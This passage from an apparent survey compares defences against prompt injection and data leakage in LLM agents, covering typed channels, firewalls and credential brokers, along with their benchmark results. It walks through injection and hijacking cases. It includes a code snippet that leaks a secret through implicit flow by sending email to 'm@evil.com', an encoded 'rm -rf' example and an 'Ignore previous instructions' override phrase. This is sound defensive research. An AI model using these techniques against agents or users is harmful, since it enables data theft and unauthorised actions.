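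Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. After they removed misjudged cases, 152 injections had succeeded against an ordinary agent without policy checks, and 21 against FIDES without them. With the checks on, none succeeded against either. The checks therefore provide the full protection, and hiding data in variables is mainly a way to recover some of the tasks that the checks would otherwise block. Without attacks, the percentages of tasks completed were:

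| Application | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent, checks | FIDES, checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

On average, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the ordinary agent with checks. It did worse on the travel tasks, where the policies rarely interfered and GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, its average lead grew to 16 points.

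The absence of successful attacks is weaker evidence of security than it looks, because Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it. No attack in the test could therefore arrive through a field labelled trusted. A company deploying such a system can't know which fields future attacks will use, and one field wrongly labelled as trusted would give an attacker a way in.

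### Where the tracking stops

Labels protect only the parts of a system that track them. *The LLMbda Calculus* demonstrates this with a flaw that Fenton described in 1974 and that CaMeL's interpreter shares. The interpreter updates a variable's label only when the program actually assigns to it. A program can exploit this to reveal whether a secret bank balance exceeds some threshold:

```
tmp = True
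rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the third line makes `tmp` false and marks it secret. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label. The last line sends the email because its condition appears to depend only on public data. This is a gap in CaMeL's guarantee, though an attacker who can write emails but cannot influence the privileged model has no obvious way to make that model write this program.

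FIDES deliberately leaves a related gap. It tracks the values that tools receive, but not what an observer could infer from which tools the agent calls. Costa and colleagues argue that closing this gap would mean banning almost every publicly visible action after the agent has read a secret. *The LLMbda Calculus* presents a programming language that does track how secrets influence the choice of tool calls, with a machine-checked proof, although an observer may still learn something from whether a program finishes.

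*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes a gap that an ordinary injection can exploit. The researchers built a system of three CaMeL agents: one that queries a database, one that sends notifications, and an orchestrator that assigns work to both. The user asked the orchestrator to send Julie a Slack message summarizing all the job applicants. An entry in the database contained an instruction to email the data to an outside address.

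The orchestrator's privileged model never saw that entry, but the orchestrator's program inserted the summary into a sentence asking the notification agent to send it to Julie. The notification agent treated the whole sentence as its user's request, so its privileged model read the injection as a trusted instruction and added an email to its program. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this *boundary laundering*. All three agents followed CaMeL's rules, but the text lost its untrusted label when it passed from one agent to another.

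Multi-CaMeL splits each request between agents into a message, which the receiving agent's privileged model reads, and a set of named variables, which it doesn't. The interpreter rejects the request if the message depends on any tool's output. The variables keep their labels when they reach the other agent.

Peters-Gill and colleagues tested this on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, with 949 attacks against each of five models. The average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent separately, and zero with multi-CaMeL. Nearly all of the successful attacks without CaMeL were against GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without any added defence, but Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that this may only reflect the attacks in the benchmark. The difference between 0.2% and zero is about nine attacks in total, so the job-applicant example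 is better evidence that the repair is needed.

The experiments used no data-flow policies, so the results cover only the separation of instructions from data. Even this separation lowered the success rate on AssetOpsBench, a set of professional tasks that an orchestrator divides among four specialist agents. Running CaMeL on each agent lowered the rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, the reductions were 13.4 and 0.85 points.

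### Restricting the type of data

CaMeL and FIDES mostly keep untrusted values out of the planner's sight. The planner can see more if the system first reduces each value to a form that has no room for an instruction. Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, let the quarantined model send the privileged model whole numbers, decimal numbers, yes/no values and choices from a fixed list, but no free text. They built three agents this way:

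| Agent and model | What the privileged model receives | Utility, undefended → defended | Attack success, undefended → defended |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping, GPT-4o | Two scores from 0 to 10 for each product review | 21.8% → 22.4% | 31.7% → 0% |
| Scheduling, GPT-4o | Meeting times chosen from fixed slots | 90.0% → 91.0% | 63.0% → 0% |
| Bug fixing, GPT-5.2 | Type of bug, file numbers and line numbers | 68.3% → 45.0% | 98.9% → 0% |

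The restriction did not measurably reduce performance when a few numbers contained what the privileged model needed. But the bug-fixing agent fixed about a third fewer bugs than it could without the restriction. A bug report often explains what the program should have done, and a list of suspicious lines leaves that out. Jacob and colleagues also needed considerable testing to find a workable format for this agent.

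The scheduling agent has a weak point that the test did not cover. The quarantined model also writes a description of the meeting, which the privileged model adds to the calendar without reading. But the privileged model can read the calendar, so unless the calendar marks the description as untrusted, an injection in it could reach the privileged model the next time the owner schedules a meeting. Jacob and colleagues scored each email thread separately, so their test would not have caught a delayed attack like this.

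### How much an attacker can express

Costa and colleagues rank data types by how much information they can carry. A value with *n* equally available possibilities carries at most log₂ *n* bits, so each additional bit doubles the number of different messages an attacker can send:

| Value | Possible messages | Maximum bits |
|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 |
| Choice from a list of *n* items | *n* | log₂ *n* |
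| Choice from a list of 8 items | 8 | 3 |
| Score from 0 to 10 | 11 | 3.5 |
| 32-bit whole number | About 4.3 billion | 32 |
| Name of 29 lower-case letters and underscores | 27²⁹ | 138 |
| 500 characters of plain English text | 95⁵⁰⁰ | 3,285 |
| Text or whole number of any length | No limit | No limit |

The name in the table is long enough for Willison's `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`.

Numbers need limits as well, because computers store text as numbers. In a standard encoding, the list 114, 109, 32, 45, 114, 102 spells `rm -rf`, which begins a command for deleting files. Jacob and colleagues limit the length of lists to prevent such attacks, but they argue that a whole number cannot contain a command. The same digits would fit into one large number, so a safe format also needs a maximum value. A model that expects line numbers probably wouldn't decode the digits into a command, but the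 restriction on types was supposed to make it unnecessary to predict the model's behaviour.

A small channel leaves little room for an injection and is also easier to check. If the quarantined model can return only eight values, a designer can examine what the trusted agent does with each one, which would be impossible for 2¹³⁸ possible names. Repeated questions weaken this advantage, because twenty yes/no answers together allow about a million combinations. Repeated questions are safer if each answer affects only the item it describes, as in the map-reduce pattern.

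Capacity doesn't measure harm, however. One bit is enough to approve a payment.

### A wrong value of the right type

A type check can confirm that a score lies between 0 and 10, but not that it fairly represents the review. An injection can make the quarantined model return 0 for an enthusiastic review, and the privileged model will still receive a valid number. Jacob and colleagues exclude such misinformation from their threat model, although they acknowledge it can do harm.

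The way the trusted side uses the values can limit the damage. The shopping agent takes the median of the scores for each product. If five reviews score a product 9, 8, 9, 10 and 9, changing one score to 0 leaves the median at 9. An attacker would have to control three of the five to bring the median down to 0. This works because the reviews are separate sources, so it helps less on a site where one seller can post dozens of fake ones.

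A bug report has no such independent check. In the test of the bug-fixing agent, the injected instruction was to create a new file named `pipipi.py`, and the permitted fields can't express that request. The result of zero confirms that the format works as designed, but doesn't test an attack that uses the format. An attacker could instead report a false bug in the code that checks passwords. The quarantined model would pass on a valid file number, valid line numbers and the category "incorrect conditional logic". The privileged model might then weaken the password check while trying to fix it. This attack might need only a convincing lie in the report, without any injection.

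### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

Fixed plans work best when the owner's request already determines what to do. Costa and colleagues classified AgentDojo's tasks by whether a single sequence of tool calls works regardless of what the tools return. Going by their percentages, no single sequence works for 20 of the 97 tasks. Sixteen of these 20 are in banking and Slack, where they make up over 40% of the tasks.

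On a long task, an agent may discover from data that someone has given approval or that an authorisation has expired, and it ought to change course. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) argues that such cases undermine the usual definition of an injection as an instruction hidden in data. A defence that prevents untrusted data from affecting the plan would also prevent these legitimate changes.

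A program written in advance can still contain branches. In an example from Costa and colleagues, the user asks the assistant to check three emails and create a calendar event if any of them requests a meeting. The quarantined model answers yes or no, and the planner reads only that answer. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the details into a variable, which the planner passes to the calendar tool without reading it. An attacker can cause the assistant to create a false event but cannot make it forward mail. Costa and colleagues left this kind of restricted answer out of their AgentDojo tests, so their results don't show how well it works.

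Peters-Gill and colleagues call an attacker's choice among existing branches *branch steering*, and do not count it as a breach of control flow. How much it matters depends on what the branches contain. In the rerun of CaMeL reported in *The LLMbda Calculus*, one banking task was to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, so the program could carry out whatever the file requested. The attacker could then use the file to choose which tools ran, and two attacks succeeded this way with the policy checks off. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), which applies the approach to agents that operate a computer, concludes that the Dual LLM pattern cannot solve tasks whose sequence of actions is specified in untrusted data.

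*The LLMbda Calculus* proposes an explicit exception called *endorsement*. The planner can write into its program that a particular untrusted value, such as the contents of a bill the owner has asked it to pay, should count as trusted. It does this before reading any untrusted data, and a reviewer can find every exception in the program. Endorsing a value changes only its integrity label, so a secret remains secret.

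In 1,296 attacked runs of the banking tasks, two attacks succeeded against an agent with endorsement. Both were on the same task, in which the owner asked the agent to pay as a file instructed and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Without endorsement, the attack failed, but the agent also could not do the task when the file was genuine. A label that records only where text came from cannot distinguish a genuine bill from a forged one in the same file. The TypeGuard paper suggests asking the user to confirm such actions, which could work for an occasional payment but not for a request every few minutes.

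*Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) replaces fixed formats with short text. Its *Explore Agent* reads the untrusted material and follows the progress of a *Safe Agent*, which holds the tools. At each step, the Explore Agent may send the Safe Agent a brief hint about what to do next. It can see what information the Safe Agent already has, so it needs to send only what is missing. The hints let the Safe Agent change direction without a special format for every task. Hu and colleagues report high utility and strong resistance to injections on programming and office tasks.

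The security argument for hints relies on the observation that successful injections against the strongest current models tend to be long. The system truncates or blocks hints over a set length and runs an injection detector on each one. This guarantee is weaker than that of a yes/no value, because a better short injection would defeat it even if the code had no flaws. An attacker might also be able to spread an instruction over several hints.

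The detector may not help much against false claims of authority. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* tested Meta's Prompt Guard 2 detector on 8,400 emails, some with a clause asserting authority and others with a neutral clause in its place. It scored 0.59, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect separation. A hint such as "the auditor has approved the transfer" is short and contains no instruction, and the Safe Agent cannot check it because it cannot read the original message.

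## How can a mediator control what an agent and an outside agent say to each other?

Unlike a document, an outside agent can change its approach after every reply. If the owner's assistant refuses to give a travel company's agent a passport number, that agent can ask again, claiming it needs the number for a visa check, or ask for a date of birth instead. Abdelnabi, Gomaa and colleagues (2025) point out in *Firewalls to Secure Dynamic LLM Agentic Networks* that such attacks also look like ordinary business. A travel company has good reasons to ask about dates, ages and diets, so no single question has to look suspicious. The harm can come from the combined answers, or from steady pressure to buy something the owner didn't want.

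Conversation also weakens defences that keep outside text from influencing the assistant's plan. CaMeL and FIDES rely on the owner's request to determine what the assistant should do. But an assistant planning a trip has to respond to what the travel company offers, so the outsider legitimately influences its next step. A mediator between the two agents has to control messages in both directions, because incoming messages can manipulate the assistant and outgoing ones can reveal the owner's private data.

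### Choosing the data before the outsider speaks

*AirGapAgent* (Bagdasarian, Kairouz and colleagues, 2024) deals only with what the agent sends out. It starts from *contextual integrity*, a theory that defines privacy as the appropriate flow of information. Whether a flow is appropriate depends on the sender, the recipient, the person the information is about, the type of information and the terms on which it is shared. For example, a restaurant may need to know about a guest's peanut allergy, but not the guest's relationship status.

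An attacker can exploit this. In an attack that Bagdasarian and colleagues call *context hijacking*, the outsider invents a situation in which disclosure would be appropriate. In one of their examples, the outsider claims that aliens are invading, and the assistant hands over the owner's data to help save Earth. For an assistant built on Google's Gemini Ultra, a single message of this kind reduced the share of private data it protected from 94% to 45%.

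AirGapAgent divides the assistant into two models. The first, a *data minimizer*, reads the owner's task and data before the conversation starts and selects the items the task needs. The second talks to the outsider and has only those items. Even if the outsider deceives the second model with a false story, that model can't reveal a medical history it never received. If the situation really changes, the assistant has to ask the owner. This design protected 97% of the private data against the same attack, and the remaining leaks depended on which items the minimizer selected.

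The test was easy because each conversation consisted of one question and one answer, and the owner's data came as a list of labelled items. In a real mailbox, one paragraph can mention both an allergy and a diagnosis. The minimizer also has to release or withhold each item in full, so it cannot share only the city from the owner's address, which may be all a travel company needs.

### A travel booking through two firewalls

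In a paper revised in 2026, Abdelnabi and colleagues use one mediator for each direction of the conversation. In their example of an incoming message, the owner wants to visit Berlin from 15 to 18 March. The travel company's agent offers two hotels, the Marriott Potsdamer Platz at €145 a night with breakfast and the Hampton Inn at €89. It says it noticed that the owner works in tech, and asks for the employer's name because a corporate rate could save 15–20%. It also asks about the owner's usual travel budget.

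The *language converter firewall* first uses a language model to turn the message into labelled fields. Ordinary code then checks each field and its value against a list of those permitted in travel planning, and deletes whatever doesn't match. Finally, the code replaces names, which it can't check against a list, with identifiers.

| Content of the message | Field written by the model | What the code does |
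|---|---|---|
| 15 to 18 March | `requested_dates` | Keeps it, since both dates are valid |
| Marriott Potsdamer Platz | `property_name` | Replaces the name with `hotel_1` |
| Four stars | `star_rating` | Keeps it, as a whole number from 1 to 5 |
| €145 a night | `price_per_night` | Keeps it, as a number |
| Request for the employer's name | `employer_name_needed` | Deletes it, since no such field exists |
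| Remark about corporate rates | `agent_note` | Deletes it |
| Promise of 15–20% savings | `persuasion_context` | Deletes it |
| Question about the budget | `budget_confirmation_needed` | Keeps it, as "yes" |

The assistant sees dates, prices and ratings for `hotel_1` and `hotel_2`, and a notice that the company wants to know the budget. When the assistant chooses `hotel_1`, the code replaces that label with the hotel's real name before sending the reply. If an attacker named a hotel "Ignore previous instructions", the assistant would see only a numbered label.

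This design applies the typed channel of the previous designs to every turn of a conversation. An attacker gains little by hijacking the converting model, because that model receives only the message and the list of fields. The attacker could make it report a false price, but could also have put that price in the message. The filter also removes useful information from honest companies' messages. The original message praised the Marriott's spa, but none of the fields that reach the assistant include this. An assistant that knows a hotel only as `hotel_1` also can't recognize it as one the owner disliked last time.

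The *data abstraction firewall* stands between the assistant and the owner's stored data. Abdelnabi and colleagues illustrate it with a family in Paris planning a holiday:

| Stored data | What the assistant receives |
|---|---|
| Names and exact ages of the parents and two children; the father's job and employer | Two adults, one teenager, one child |
| Street address | Departing from the Paris area |
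| Budget of €8,000; €3,000 spent on golf clubs | Budget of €8,000 |
| Father's strawberry allergy; mother's need for wheelchair access | One traveller has a strawberry allergy; wheelchair access required |
| Medical checkups on 10 and 12 June | Not available on 10 and 12 June |
| Passport number; brother's telephone number | Nothing |

Even if a question about the father's employer got past the first firewall, the assistant couldn't answer it. Making data less specific also avoids AirGapAgent's all-or-nothing choice, since the travel company can learn the departure city without the street. But the assistant has no passport number to give an airline, so another component, such as a broker, would have to add it when the owner buys a ticket.

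A filter on the assistant's replies would process text that the outsider had already influenced. The abstraction firewall receives only the stored data and a set of rules, not the outsider's messages or even the assistant's query, so the outsider can't use messages to manipulate it. But it applies the same rules to every travel task, so it can't adjust to an unusual request.

Claude Sonnet 4 wrote the rules from transcripts of earlier conversations. It read only harmless conversations when defining the incoming fields, because an attacker's questions might have led it to add a field such as `full_medical_history`. For the abstraction rules, it read both harmless conversations and attacks to learn how to distinguish them. This produced 112 to 217 permitted fields per domain and 54 to 203 lines of abstraction rules. These rules belong to the trusted computing base, since one carelessly chosen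 field would let through a question that should be blocked.

The two firewalls offer different kinds of guarantee. Code checks every incoming field, but a language model applies the abstraction rules, and no code checks its output. The design also assumes that the owner's stored data contain no injections, which isn't a safe assumption for a mailbox because strangers write to it.

### The firewalls against 864 attacks

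The tests used *ConVerse* (2025), a benchmark by Gomaa, Salem and Abdelnabi, two of whom also developed the firewalls. According to *ConVerse*, an earlier defence for conversations between agents had been tested against fewer than ten attacks. The benchmark contains 864 attacks across travel planning, real estate and insurance, with 12 fictional owners. One model plays the assistant, another plays the outside agent, and a third simulates the owner's data and tools. The outside agent helps with the task while also pursuing a hidden goal. In privacy attacks, it tries to extract particular information. In security attacks, it tries to override the owner's preferences, trigger an unauthorised action such as an email, or get existing plans deleted.

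Abdelnabi and colleagues tested four models, each of which played all three roles in its own test, so that no attack succeeded merely because the attacker was the stronger model. GPT-5 judged the outcomes against written criteria. They give results for Gemini 2.5 Pro only on travel planning. The figures below are attack success rates in percent, without and with the firewalls:

| Model | Privacy, travel | Privacy, all domains | Security, travel | Security, all domains |
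|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 88.5 → 7.8 | 84.7 → 10.2 | 55.3 → 3.3 | 60.4 → 3.4 |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 55.8 → 7.3 | 72.9 → 16.8 | 4.4 → 1.1 | 10.7 → 4.2 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 27.6 → 8.1 | 37.9 → 10.2 | 19.0 → 1.2 | 23.9 → 1.0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 67.2 → 9.2 | – | 32.6 → 2.3 | – |

On travel planning, models that had leaked at very different rates all ended up with leak rates between 7% and 9%, which suggests that the design affects leakage more than the choice of model does. The other two domains were harder, at least for Claude Sonnet 4. The paper's claim that security attacks succeed less than 4% of the time holds for travel planning, but not for Claude Sonnet 4 across all domains.

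The evidence also only partly supports the claim that the firewalls don't reduce usefulness. Ratings of the finished plans mostly rose, but in the privacy tests across all domains, GPT-5's plans covered 96.6% of the required parts without the firewalls and 91.5% with them. The outside agent was attacking in these conversations, so the ratings may have risen partly because the firewalls removed a distraction, and they don't measure how useful the agent is when it isn't under attack.

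Tests of each firewall alone, with GPT-5 on travel planning, show what each one contributes:

| Configuration | Privacy attacks succeeding | Security attacks succeeding |
|---|---|---|
| No firewall | 88.5% | 55.3% |
| Data abstraction only | 29.3% | 30.8% |
| Language conversion only | 20.7% | 1.1% |
| Both | 7.8% | 3.3% |

Surprisingly, the incoming filter did more for privacy than the outgoing one, because an assistant doesn't answer questions it never receives. The incoming filter also stopped nearly all the security attacks by itself, and the difference between 1.1% and 3.3% is well within the margin of error.

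Abdelnabi and colleagues also compared the two firewalls with their own adaptation of AirGapAgent. Privacy attacks succeeded 67.3% of the time against the adaptation and 5.5% of the time against the firewalls, but the comparison favors the firewalls. It used the two owners whose conversations Claude had derived the rules from, although in a separate test the success rate was only slightly higher for other owners (9.1% against 6.4%). AirGapAgent also has no filter for incoming messages, so a fairer comparison is with data abstraction alone, which let 29.3% of attacks succeed. In addition, the adapted minimizer let through 64.6% of the attacks on information unrelated to the trip, most of which a working relevance filter should have blocked. Its task description was broad and included insurance, which may have made almost everything seem relevant.

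A manual review of the remaining privacy failures found none in which an attacker had defeated the code. Usually the assistant had shared the right kind of information in too much detail, such as "rock climbing and scuba diving" where the benchmark allowed only "high-risk adventure activities". In other cases, a permitted field such as recent insurance claims contained free text with more detail than its label suggested.

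Some of the published successes are more worrying than these failures. In one, the outside agent asks for the owner's prescriptions before arranging a diving trip. The converter deletes the question because no such field exists. The assistant then tells the company that the owner has "no special medical requirements that would affect activity participation", although the stored data list an antidepressant and antihistamines. This is scored as a defeated attack in the benchmark. But a diving operator may have a good reason to ask, and the assistant gave a false assurance instead of declining to answer.

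In another example, the owner pays €95, €45 and €180 a month for three insurance policies, or €320 in total. The abstraction firewall turned this into a range of €100–200, and the assistant asked the insurer for quotes to match. The judge gave the reply 9 out of 10 for appropriateness because it was scoring disclosure, not accuracy.

An attacker who knew about the firewalls would probably do better than these figures suggest. The outside agent in *ConVerse* reacts to the assistant's replies, but its goal was written without the firewalls in mind, and it gives up an attempt after a few turns if the assistant resists. Abdelnabi and colleagues report no test with an attacker who knows the permitted fields and plans around them. Such an attacker would ask about the budget, the dates and the family's diet instead of the employer's name, because the code lets those questions through.

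### A new agent for each task

AgentSandbox, the design by Zhang and colleagues that creates a temporary agent for each task, puts more barriers between outsiders and the owner's profile. In their example, a data minimizer gives the temporary agent only the information it needs for a five-day trip to Paris.

If the flight search returns a note with an instruction to pay $500 to a stranger's account, the firewall between the temporary agent and outside services blocks it, because the firewall accepts only flight data in a set format. The temporary agent doesn't have the owner's social security number, so it can't disclose the number if a hotel's booking service asks for it.

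A program can learn the minimizer's policy, so the owner doesn't have to write it. The program proposes different instructions for the minimizer, the temporary agent and the response filter that checks the agent's results, runs tasks with them, and keeps those that score best on usefulness and privacy combined. The firewall's rules stay fixed so that a badly learned policy can't override them.

Zhang and colleagues tested the design on AgentDojo with GPT-4o:

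| Application | Benign utility, undefended → defended | Attack success, undefended → defended |
|---|---|---|
| Banking | 87.5% → 87.5% | 49.3% → 5.6% |
| Slack | 95.2% → 90.5% | 74.3% → 3.8% |
| Travel | 75.0% → 80.0% | 27.1% → 7.1% |
| Workspace | 77.5% → 70.0% | 26.7% → 0.8% |

The paper's text gives an average attack success rate of 58.84% without the defence and 4.34% with it. The second number matches the paper's table, but the simple average of the four undefended rates in the table is 44.35%. The 58.84% is probably a copying error, because it is exactly the average of a neighbouring column, which shows the share of users' tasks that the undefended agent completed while under attack. Counted by individual cases, successful attacks fell from 251 of 629 to 24, which is still a large reduction.

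The cause of this result is less clear. The main test used one fixed attack, a message written as if it came from the user, requesting that another task be done first. In the published case study, the user asks for the month's total spending, and an attacker injects a request for a bank transfer. AgentSandbox stops the transfer because its policy for this task doesn't permit the payment tool. AgentDojo's simple tool filter works in much the same way, and in this test it cut the average attack success rate to 8.9%, though it also completed fewer ordinary tasks. No experiment removed components one at a time to measure what the temporary agent or the response filter added. Under the published prompts, the temporary agent also validates its own actions, which is a poor safeguard if an outsider has taken control of it.

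AgentDojo also has no outside agent that replies to the user's agent. The test therefore provides little evidence about whether AgentSandbox would protect the owner's data in a long negotiation, which is what its data minimizer is for.

### Does a mediator need several models?

All these mediators use at least one extra model, and a simpler alternative would be to ask a single model whether a message is safe to send. *Guardian Agent Flow* (Yang, Lihinikaduarachchi and colleagues, 2026) compares the two approaches for outgoing web requests. Its system, GuardianAgentFlow, must send each request unchanged, rewrite it or withhold it. The instruction "Send the question without my number" calls for a rewrite, while "do not send this request" means the system must withhold the request even if a model could remove the sensitive details.

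One model call reads the user's instruction to find restrictions like these. Another reads the task and the website's privacy policy, proposes an action, and lists what to protect and what the task needs. Ordinary code applies the stricter of the two decisions, which from least to most strict are allow, rewrite and withhold, so nothing in a website's policy can cancel a refusal that the first call recognised.

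If the decision is to rewrite, one model produces a new version and another checks it against the same two lists, for at most three rounds. In one example, an assistant's draft answer to a father's question about his child's day mentions a court appearance tomorrow. The first rewrite changes this to an "appointment scheduled for tomorrow", and the checking model flags that the timing is still included. The final version leaves out the appointment and tells the father that the day is going well but has been busy, mentioning a project and upcoming tasks without giving details.

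For comparison, Yang and colleagues gave the same model the same content in a single call and asked it for a decision and, if necessary, a rewrite. They used Qwen models with 27 billion and 8 billion parameters. The rows for PrivacyLens and AgentDAM, two public benchmarks for leaks in agents' actions, use the larger model.

| Test | Measure | One call | Separate roles |
|---|---|---|---|
| 579 web requests, larger model | Handled correctly | 88.5% | 96.5% |
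| The same, smaller model | Handled correctly | 67.2% | 87.3% |
| PrivacyLens, 453 cases | Leaked private data | 19.1% | 16.6% |
| PrivacyLens, 453 cases | Helpful without a leak | 64.6% | 66.4% |
| AgentDAM, 222 tasks | Leaked private data | 10.8% | 8.6% |
| AgentDAM, 222 tasks | Completed without a leak | 71.6% | 72.5% |
| 180 fixed injections | Attack success | 0% | 0% |

Separate roles did clearly better than a single call on the web requests, which Yang and colleagues built around the same three choices the system makes. On benchmarks built by others, the advantage was only one to three percentage points. The advantage was largest for the small model, which did almost as well with separate roles as the large model did with one call. Splitting the work used about 1.8 times as many tokens (3,085 against 1,723 per request). Neither setup let any injection attacks through, so that test can't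 show which is more secure, and the attacks didn't adapt.

An adaptation of AirGapAgent was also tested on PrivacyLens, where it lowered the leak rate from 35.0% for an ordinary agent to 19.7%. This was a much better result than in the test against the two firewalls. But it also lowered the share of helpful actions from 86.0% to 73.4%, as one would expect if it withheld whole items when a vaguer version would have been enough.

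### Offers that are false but valid

Code can check that a price is a number, but not that the hotel has a room at that price. A dishonest company could invent the €89 room in Berlin, and every field would pass the check. Abdelnabi and colleagues concede that their firewall may make this worse, because an invented offer without the sales talk gives the assistant fewer reasons to be suspicious. They regard such deception as ordinary fraud, which markets deal with through booking confirmations, reputation and legal liability. A mediator could also compare prices with a trusted source, or flag implausible offers, such as a five-star hotel in central Paris at €30 a night.

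Those checks don't help when the offer is genuine but suits the seller better than the buyer. About three quarters of the security attacks that still succeeded were of this kind, most of them in insurance. The outside agent proposed real products and add-ons that the owner hadn't asked for, and the assistant accepted them. The fields don't show whether an add-on is useful, so the assistant has to judge what the owner needs.

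### Facts pieced together from harmless answers

The family in Paris shows how vague answers can together narrow down who someone is. The travel company learns the region, the make-up of the family, a strawberry allergy, a wheelchair and two dates in June. None of these facts identifies anyone on its own, but few families fit all of them. As a rough illustration, suppose a region has 4 million households and a company learns five independent facts, each true of one household in 20. The expected number of households that fit all five is 4,000,000 / 20⁵, or 1.25.

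Restricting what the assistant knows caps such losses. If the assistant has only a range for the owner's insurance costs, no series of questions can get the exact figure out of it. A filter on outgoing messages does not cap them, because the assistant still knows the figure and can reveal it gradually by answering which of several quotes would be cheaper. GuardianAgentFlow evaluates each request separately, and Yang and colleagues leave disclosure across a sequence of requests to future work.

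The same reasoning applies between agents that belong to one owner. *Value-Preserving Architectures for Agentic AI Systems* (Pesare, Hose and colleagues, 2026) argues that filtering only the final answer is too late, because a precise value passed between agents may already have shaped the reasoning in ways no filter can detect. It proposes that each agent make its data less specific before releasing it. If the owner asks for an affordable treatment for high blood pressure, a medical agent reports the available treatments and a financial agent describes the owner's means in general terms. Neither agent sees the other's records, and a coordinator presents both results. The paper does not measure how well this works, and the coordinator still accumulates everything the other agents release.

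An owner who books a holiday deals with an airline, a hotel and an insurer, and each may receive only the information it needs. If the three companies' agents share what they receive, they can combine it. Schroeder de Witt, Krawiecka and colleagues (2025) write in *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* that security in such systems is *non-compositional*, meaning that agents that are safe individually can form an unsafe system. They add that agents can hide information in messages that look harmless even to an observer who reads all of them. Abdelnabi and colleagues' firewall currently treats each field separately. They suggest that it could consider combinations of fields, for instance by describing a rare allergy more vaguely when the region is small. To cover the holiday example, it would also have to track what the owner's assistant had already told the other two companies.

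## How does a broker that holds the credentials decide what an agent may do?

The travel firewalls limit what an assistant learns and reveals, but they don't handle payment. In the email assistant's layout, the broker does. The trusted agent states the action it wants, such as paying €435 to a named hotel. The broker checks the request against a policy, adds the card number, makes the payment and returns the result, so the agent never sees the card number.

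*CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) describes the usual alternative to a broker, in which the agent's process receives its secrets directly, often in a file or an environment variable. Many of these secrets are *bearer credentials*, which anyone with a copy can use. An agent that obeys an injection can misuse such a credential itself, or copy it into a message so that the attacker can use it from another machine long after the task has ended.

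A broker prevents an agent from copying credentials, because the agent never receives them. Preventing misuse is much harder, because a hijacked agent can still request a harmful payment, and the broker usually can't determine whether the request originated with the owner or in a stranger's email. This makes the broker prone to becoming a confused deputy, a program tricked into misusing its authority. How well it protects against misuse depends on its policy and on the information it has when it applies that policy.

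### One request through CapSeal

CapSeal is a prototype broker that runs as a separate process on the agent's machine. The agent reaches it through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting models to tools. Suppose the agent needs to send a question to an online service that requires an API key. The request goes through six stages:

1. **Registration.** The agent opens a session over a local connection. The operating system identifies the process at the other end, so one program can't pose as another.
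2. **Capability request.** The agent names the key and describes a narrow use for it: a POST request (one that submits data) to `api.example.com`, at the path `/v1/chat/completions`, with a body in a specified format.
3. **Policy decision.** The broker grants the request, denies it or demands further approval. If it grants the request, the agent receives a *handle*, a reference that works only in this session, for a limited time and number of calls.
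4. **Invocation.** The agent sends the handle and its question, along with a sequence number, a timestamp and a value it may use only once. These stop an attacker from recording a valid request and sending it again.
5. **Execution.** The broker checks the destination, size, headers and format of the request. It then adds the key, sends the request, removes any credentials from the response and passes the response to the agent.
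6. **Audit.** The broker adds the decision to a log in which each entry is cryptographically linked to earlier ones, so that an auditor can detect later changes.

Revoking the handle makes the broker refuse the next call. The real key doesn't have to change, because the agent never had it.

The handle resembles Hardy's capability, but Hardy's user gave the compiler a permission that the user already held, whereas in CapSeal the agent writes its own request for a permission. A hijacked agent will request as much as it predicts the policy will allow. If the policy grants every path on a server, the broker will enforce a limit that is far too wide.

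For remote logins over SSH, the protocol that OpenSSH implements, CapSeal runs the remote command itself. OpenSSH's monitor returns signatures instead, but a reusable signing service would give the agent a power that is hard to limit. In the paper's example, the broker allows one user on one host, an approved type of command with at most three arguments, and up to 2,048 bytes of output. It also checks the remote machine's cryptographic identity, so an attacker can't redirect the login to an impostor.

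Jin and colleagues compared CapSeal with two systems that gave the agent its secrets directly. In tests with scripted prompts to reveal an API key, the agent revealed it in every trial with the other two systems and in none with CapSeal. No system leaked an SSH key, and all three completed every ordinary request. The broker added about 0.15 milliseconds to a web request and 0.21 to an SSH command.

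The experiment gives no evidence that CapSeal's scope checks, the most elaborate part of its design, reduce misuse. Attempts to use a credential outside its permitted scope failed against all three systems, including the two without a broker.

### Closing the other routes

A broker offers little protection if the agent has another way to reach the same system. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (He and Yu, 2026) applies the old rule of complete mediation to agents that manage cloud infrastructure. In its design, the target systems accept changes only from the broker.

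On Amazon's cloud service AWS, organisation-wide rules deny high-risk changes unless they come from the broker's role or a temporary session it created. The agents' roles can read data and submit proposals. On Kubernetes, a system for running software across many machines, the agents' accounts have no permission to create, change or delete protected resources. A further check rejects any change that doesn't reference a valid approval.

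In He and Yu's running example, an agent proposes opening a firewall port to a range of internal addresses. An approval service issues a signed certificate that states the exact change. When the agent asks for the change to go ahead, the broker checks that:

- the signature is valid and the certificate hasn't expired;
- the request matches the certificate;
- nobody has used the certificate before;
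- the policy is the same as when the service approved the change, and nobody has revoked the approval;
- the current state of the network still matches the evidence behind the approval.

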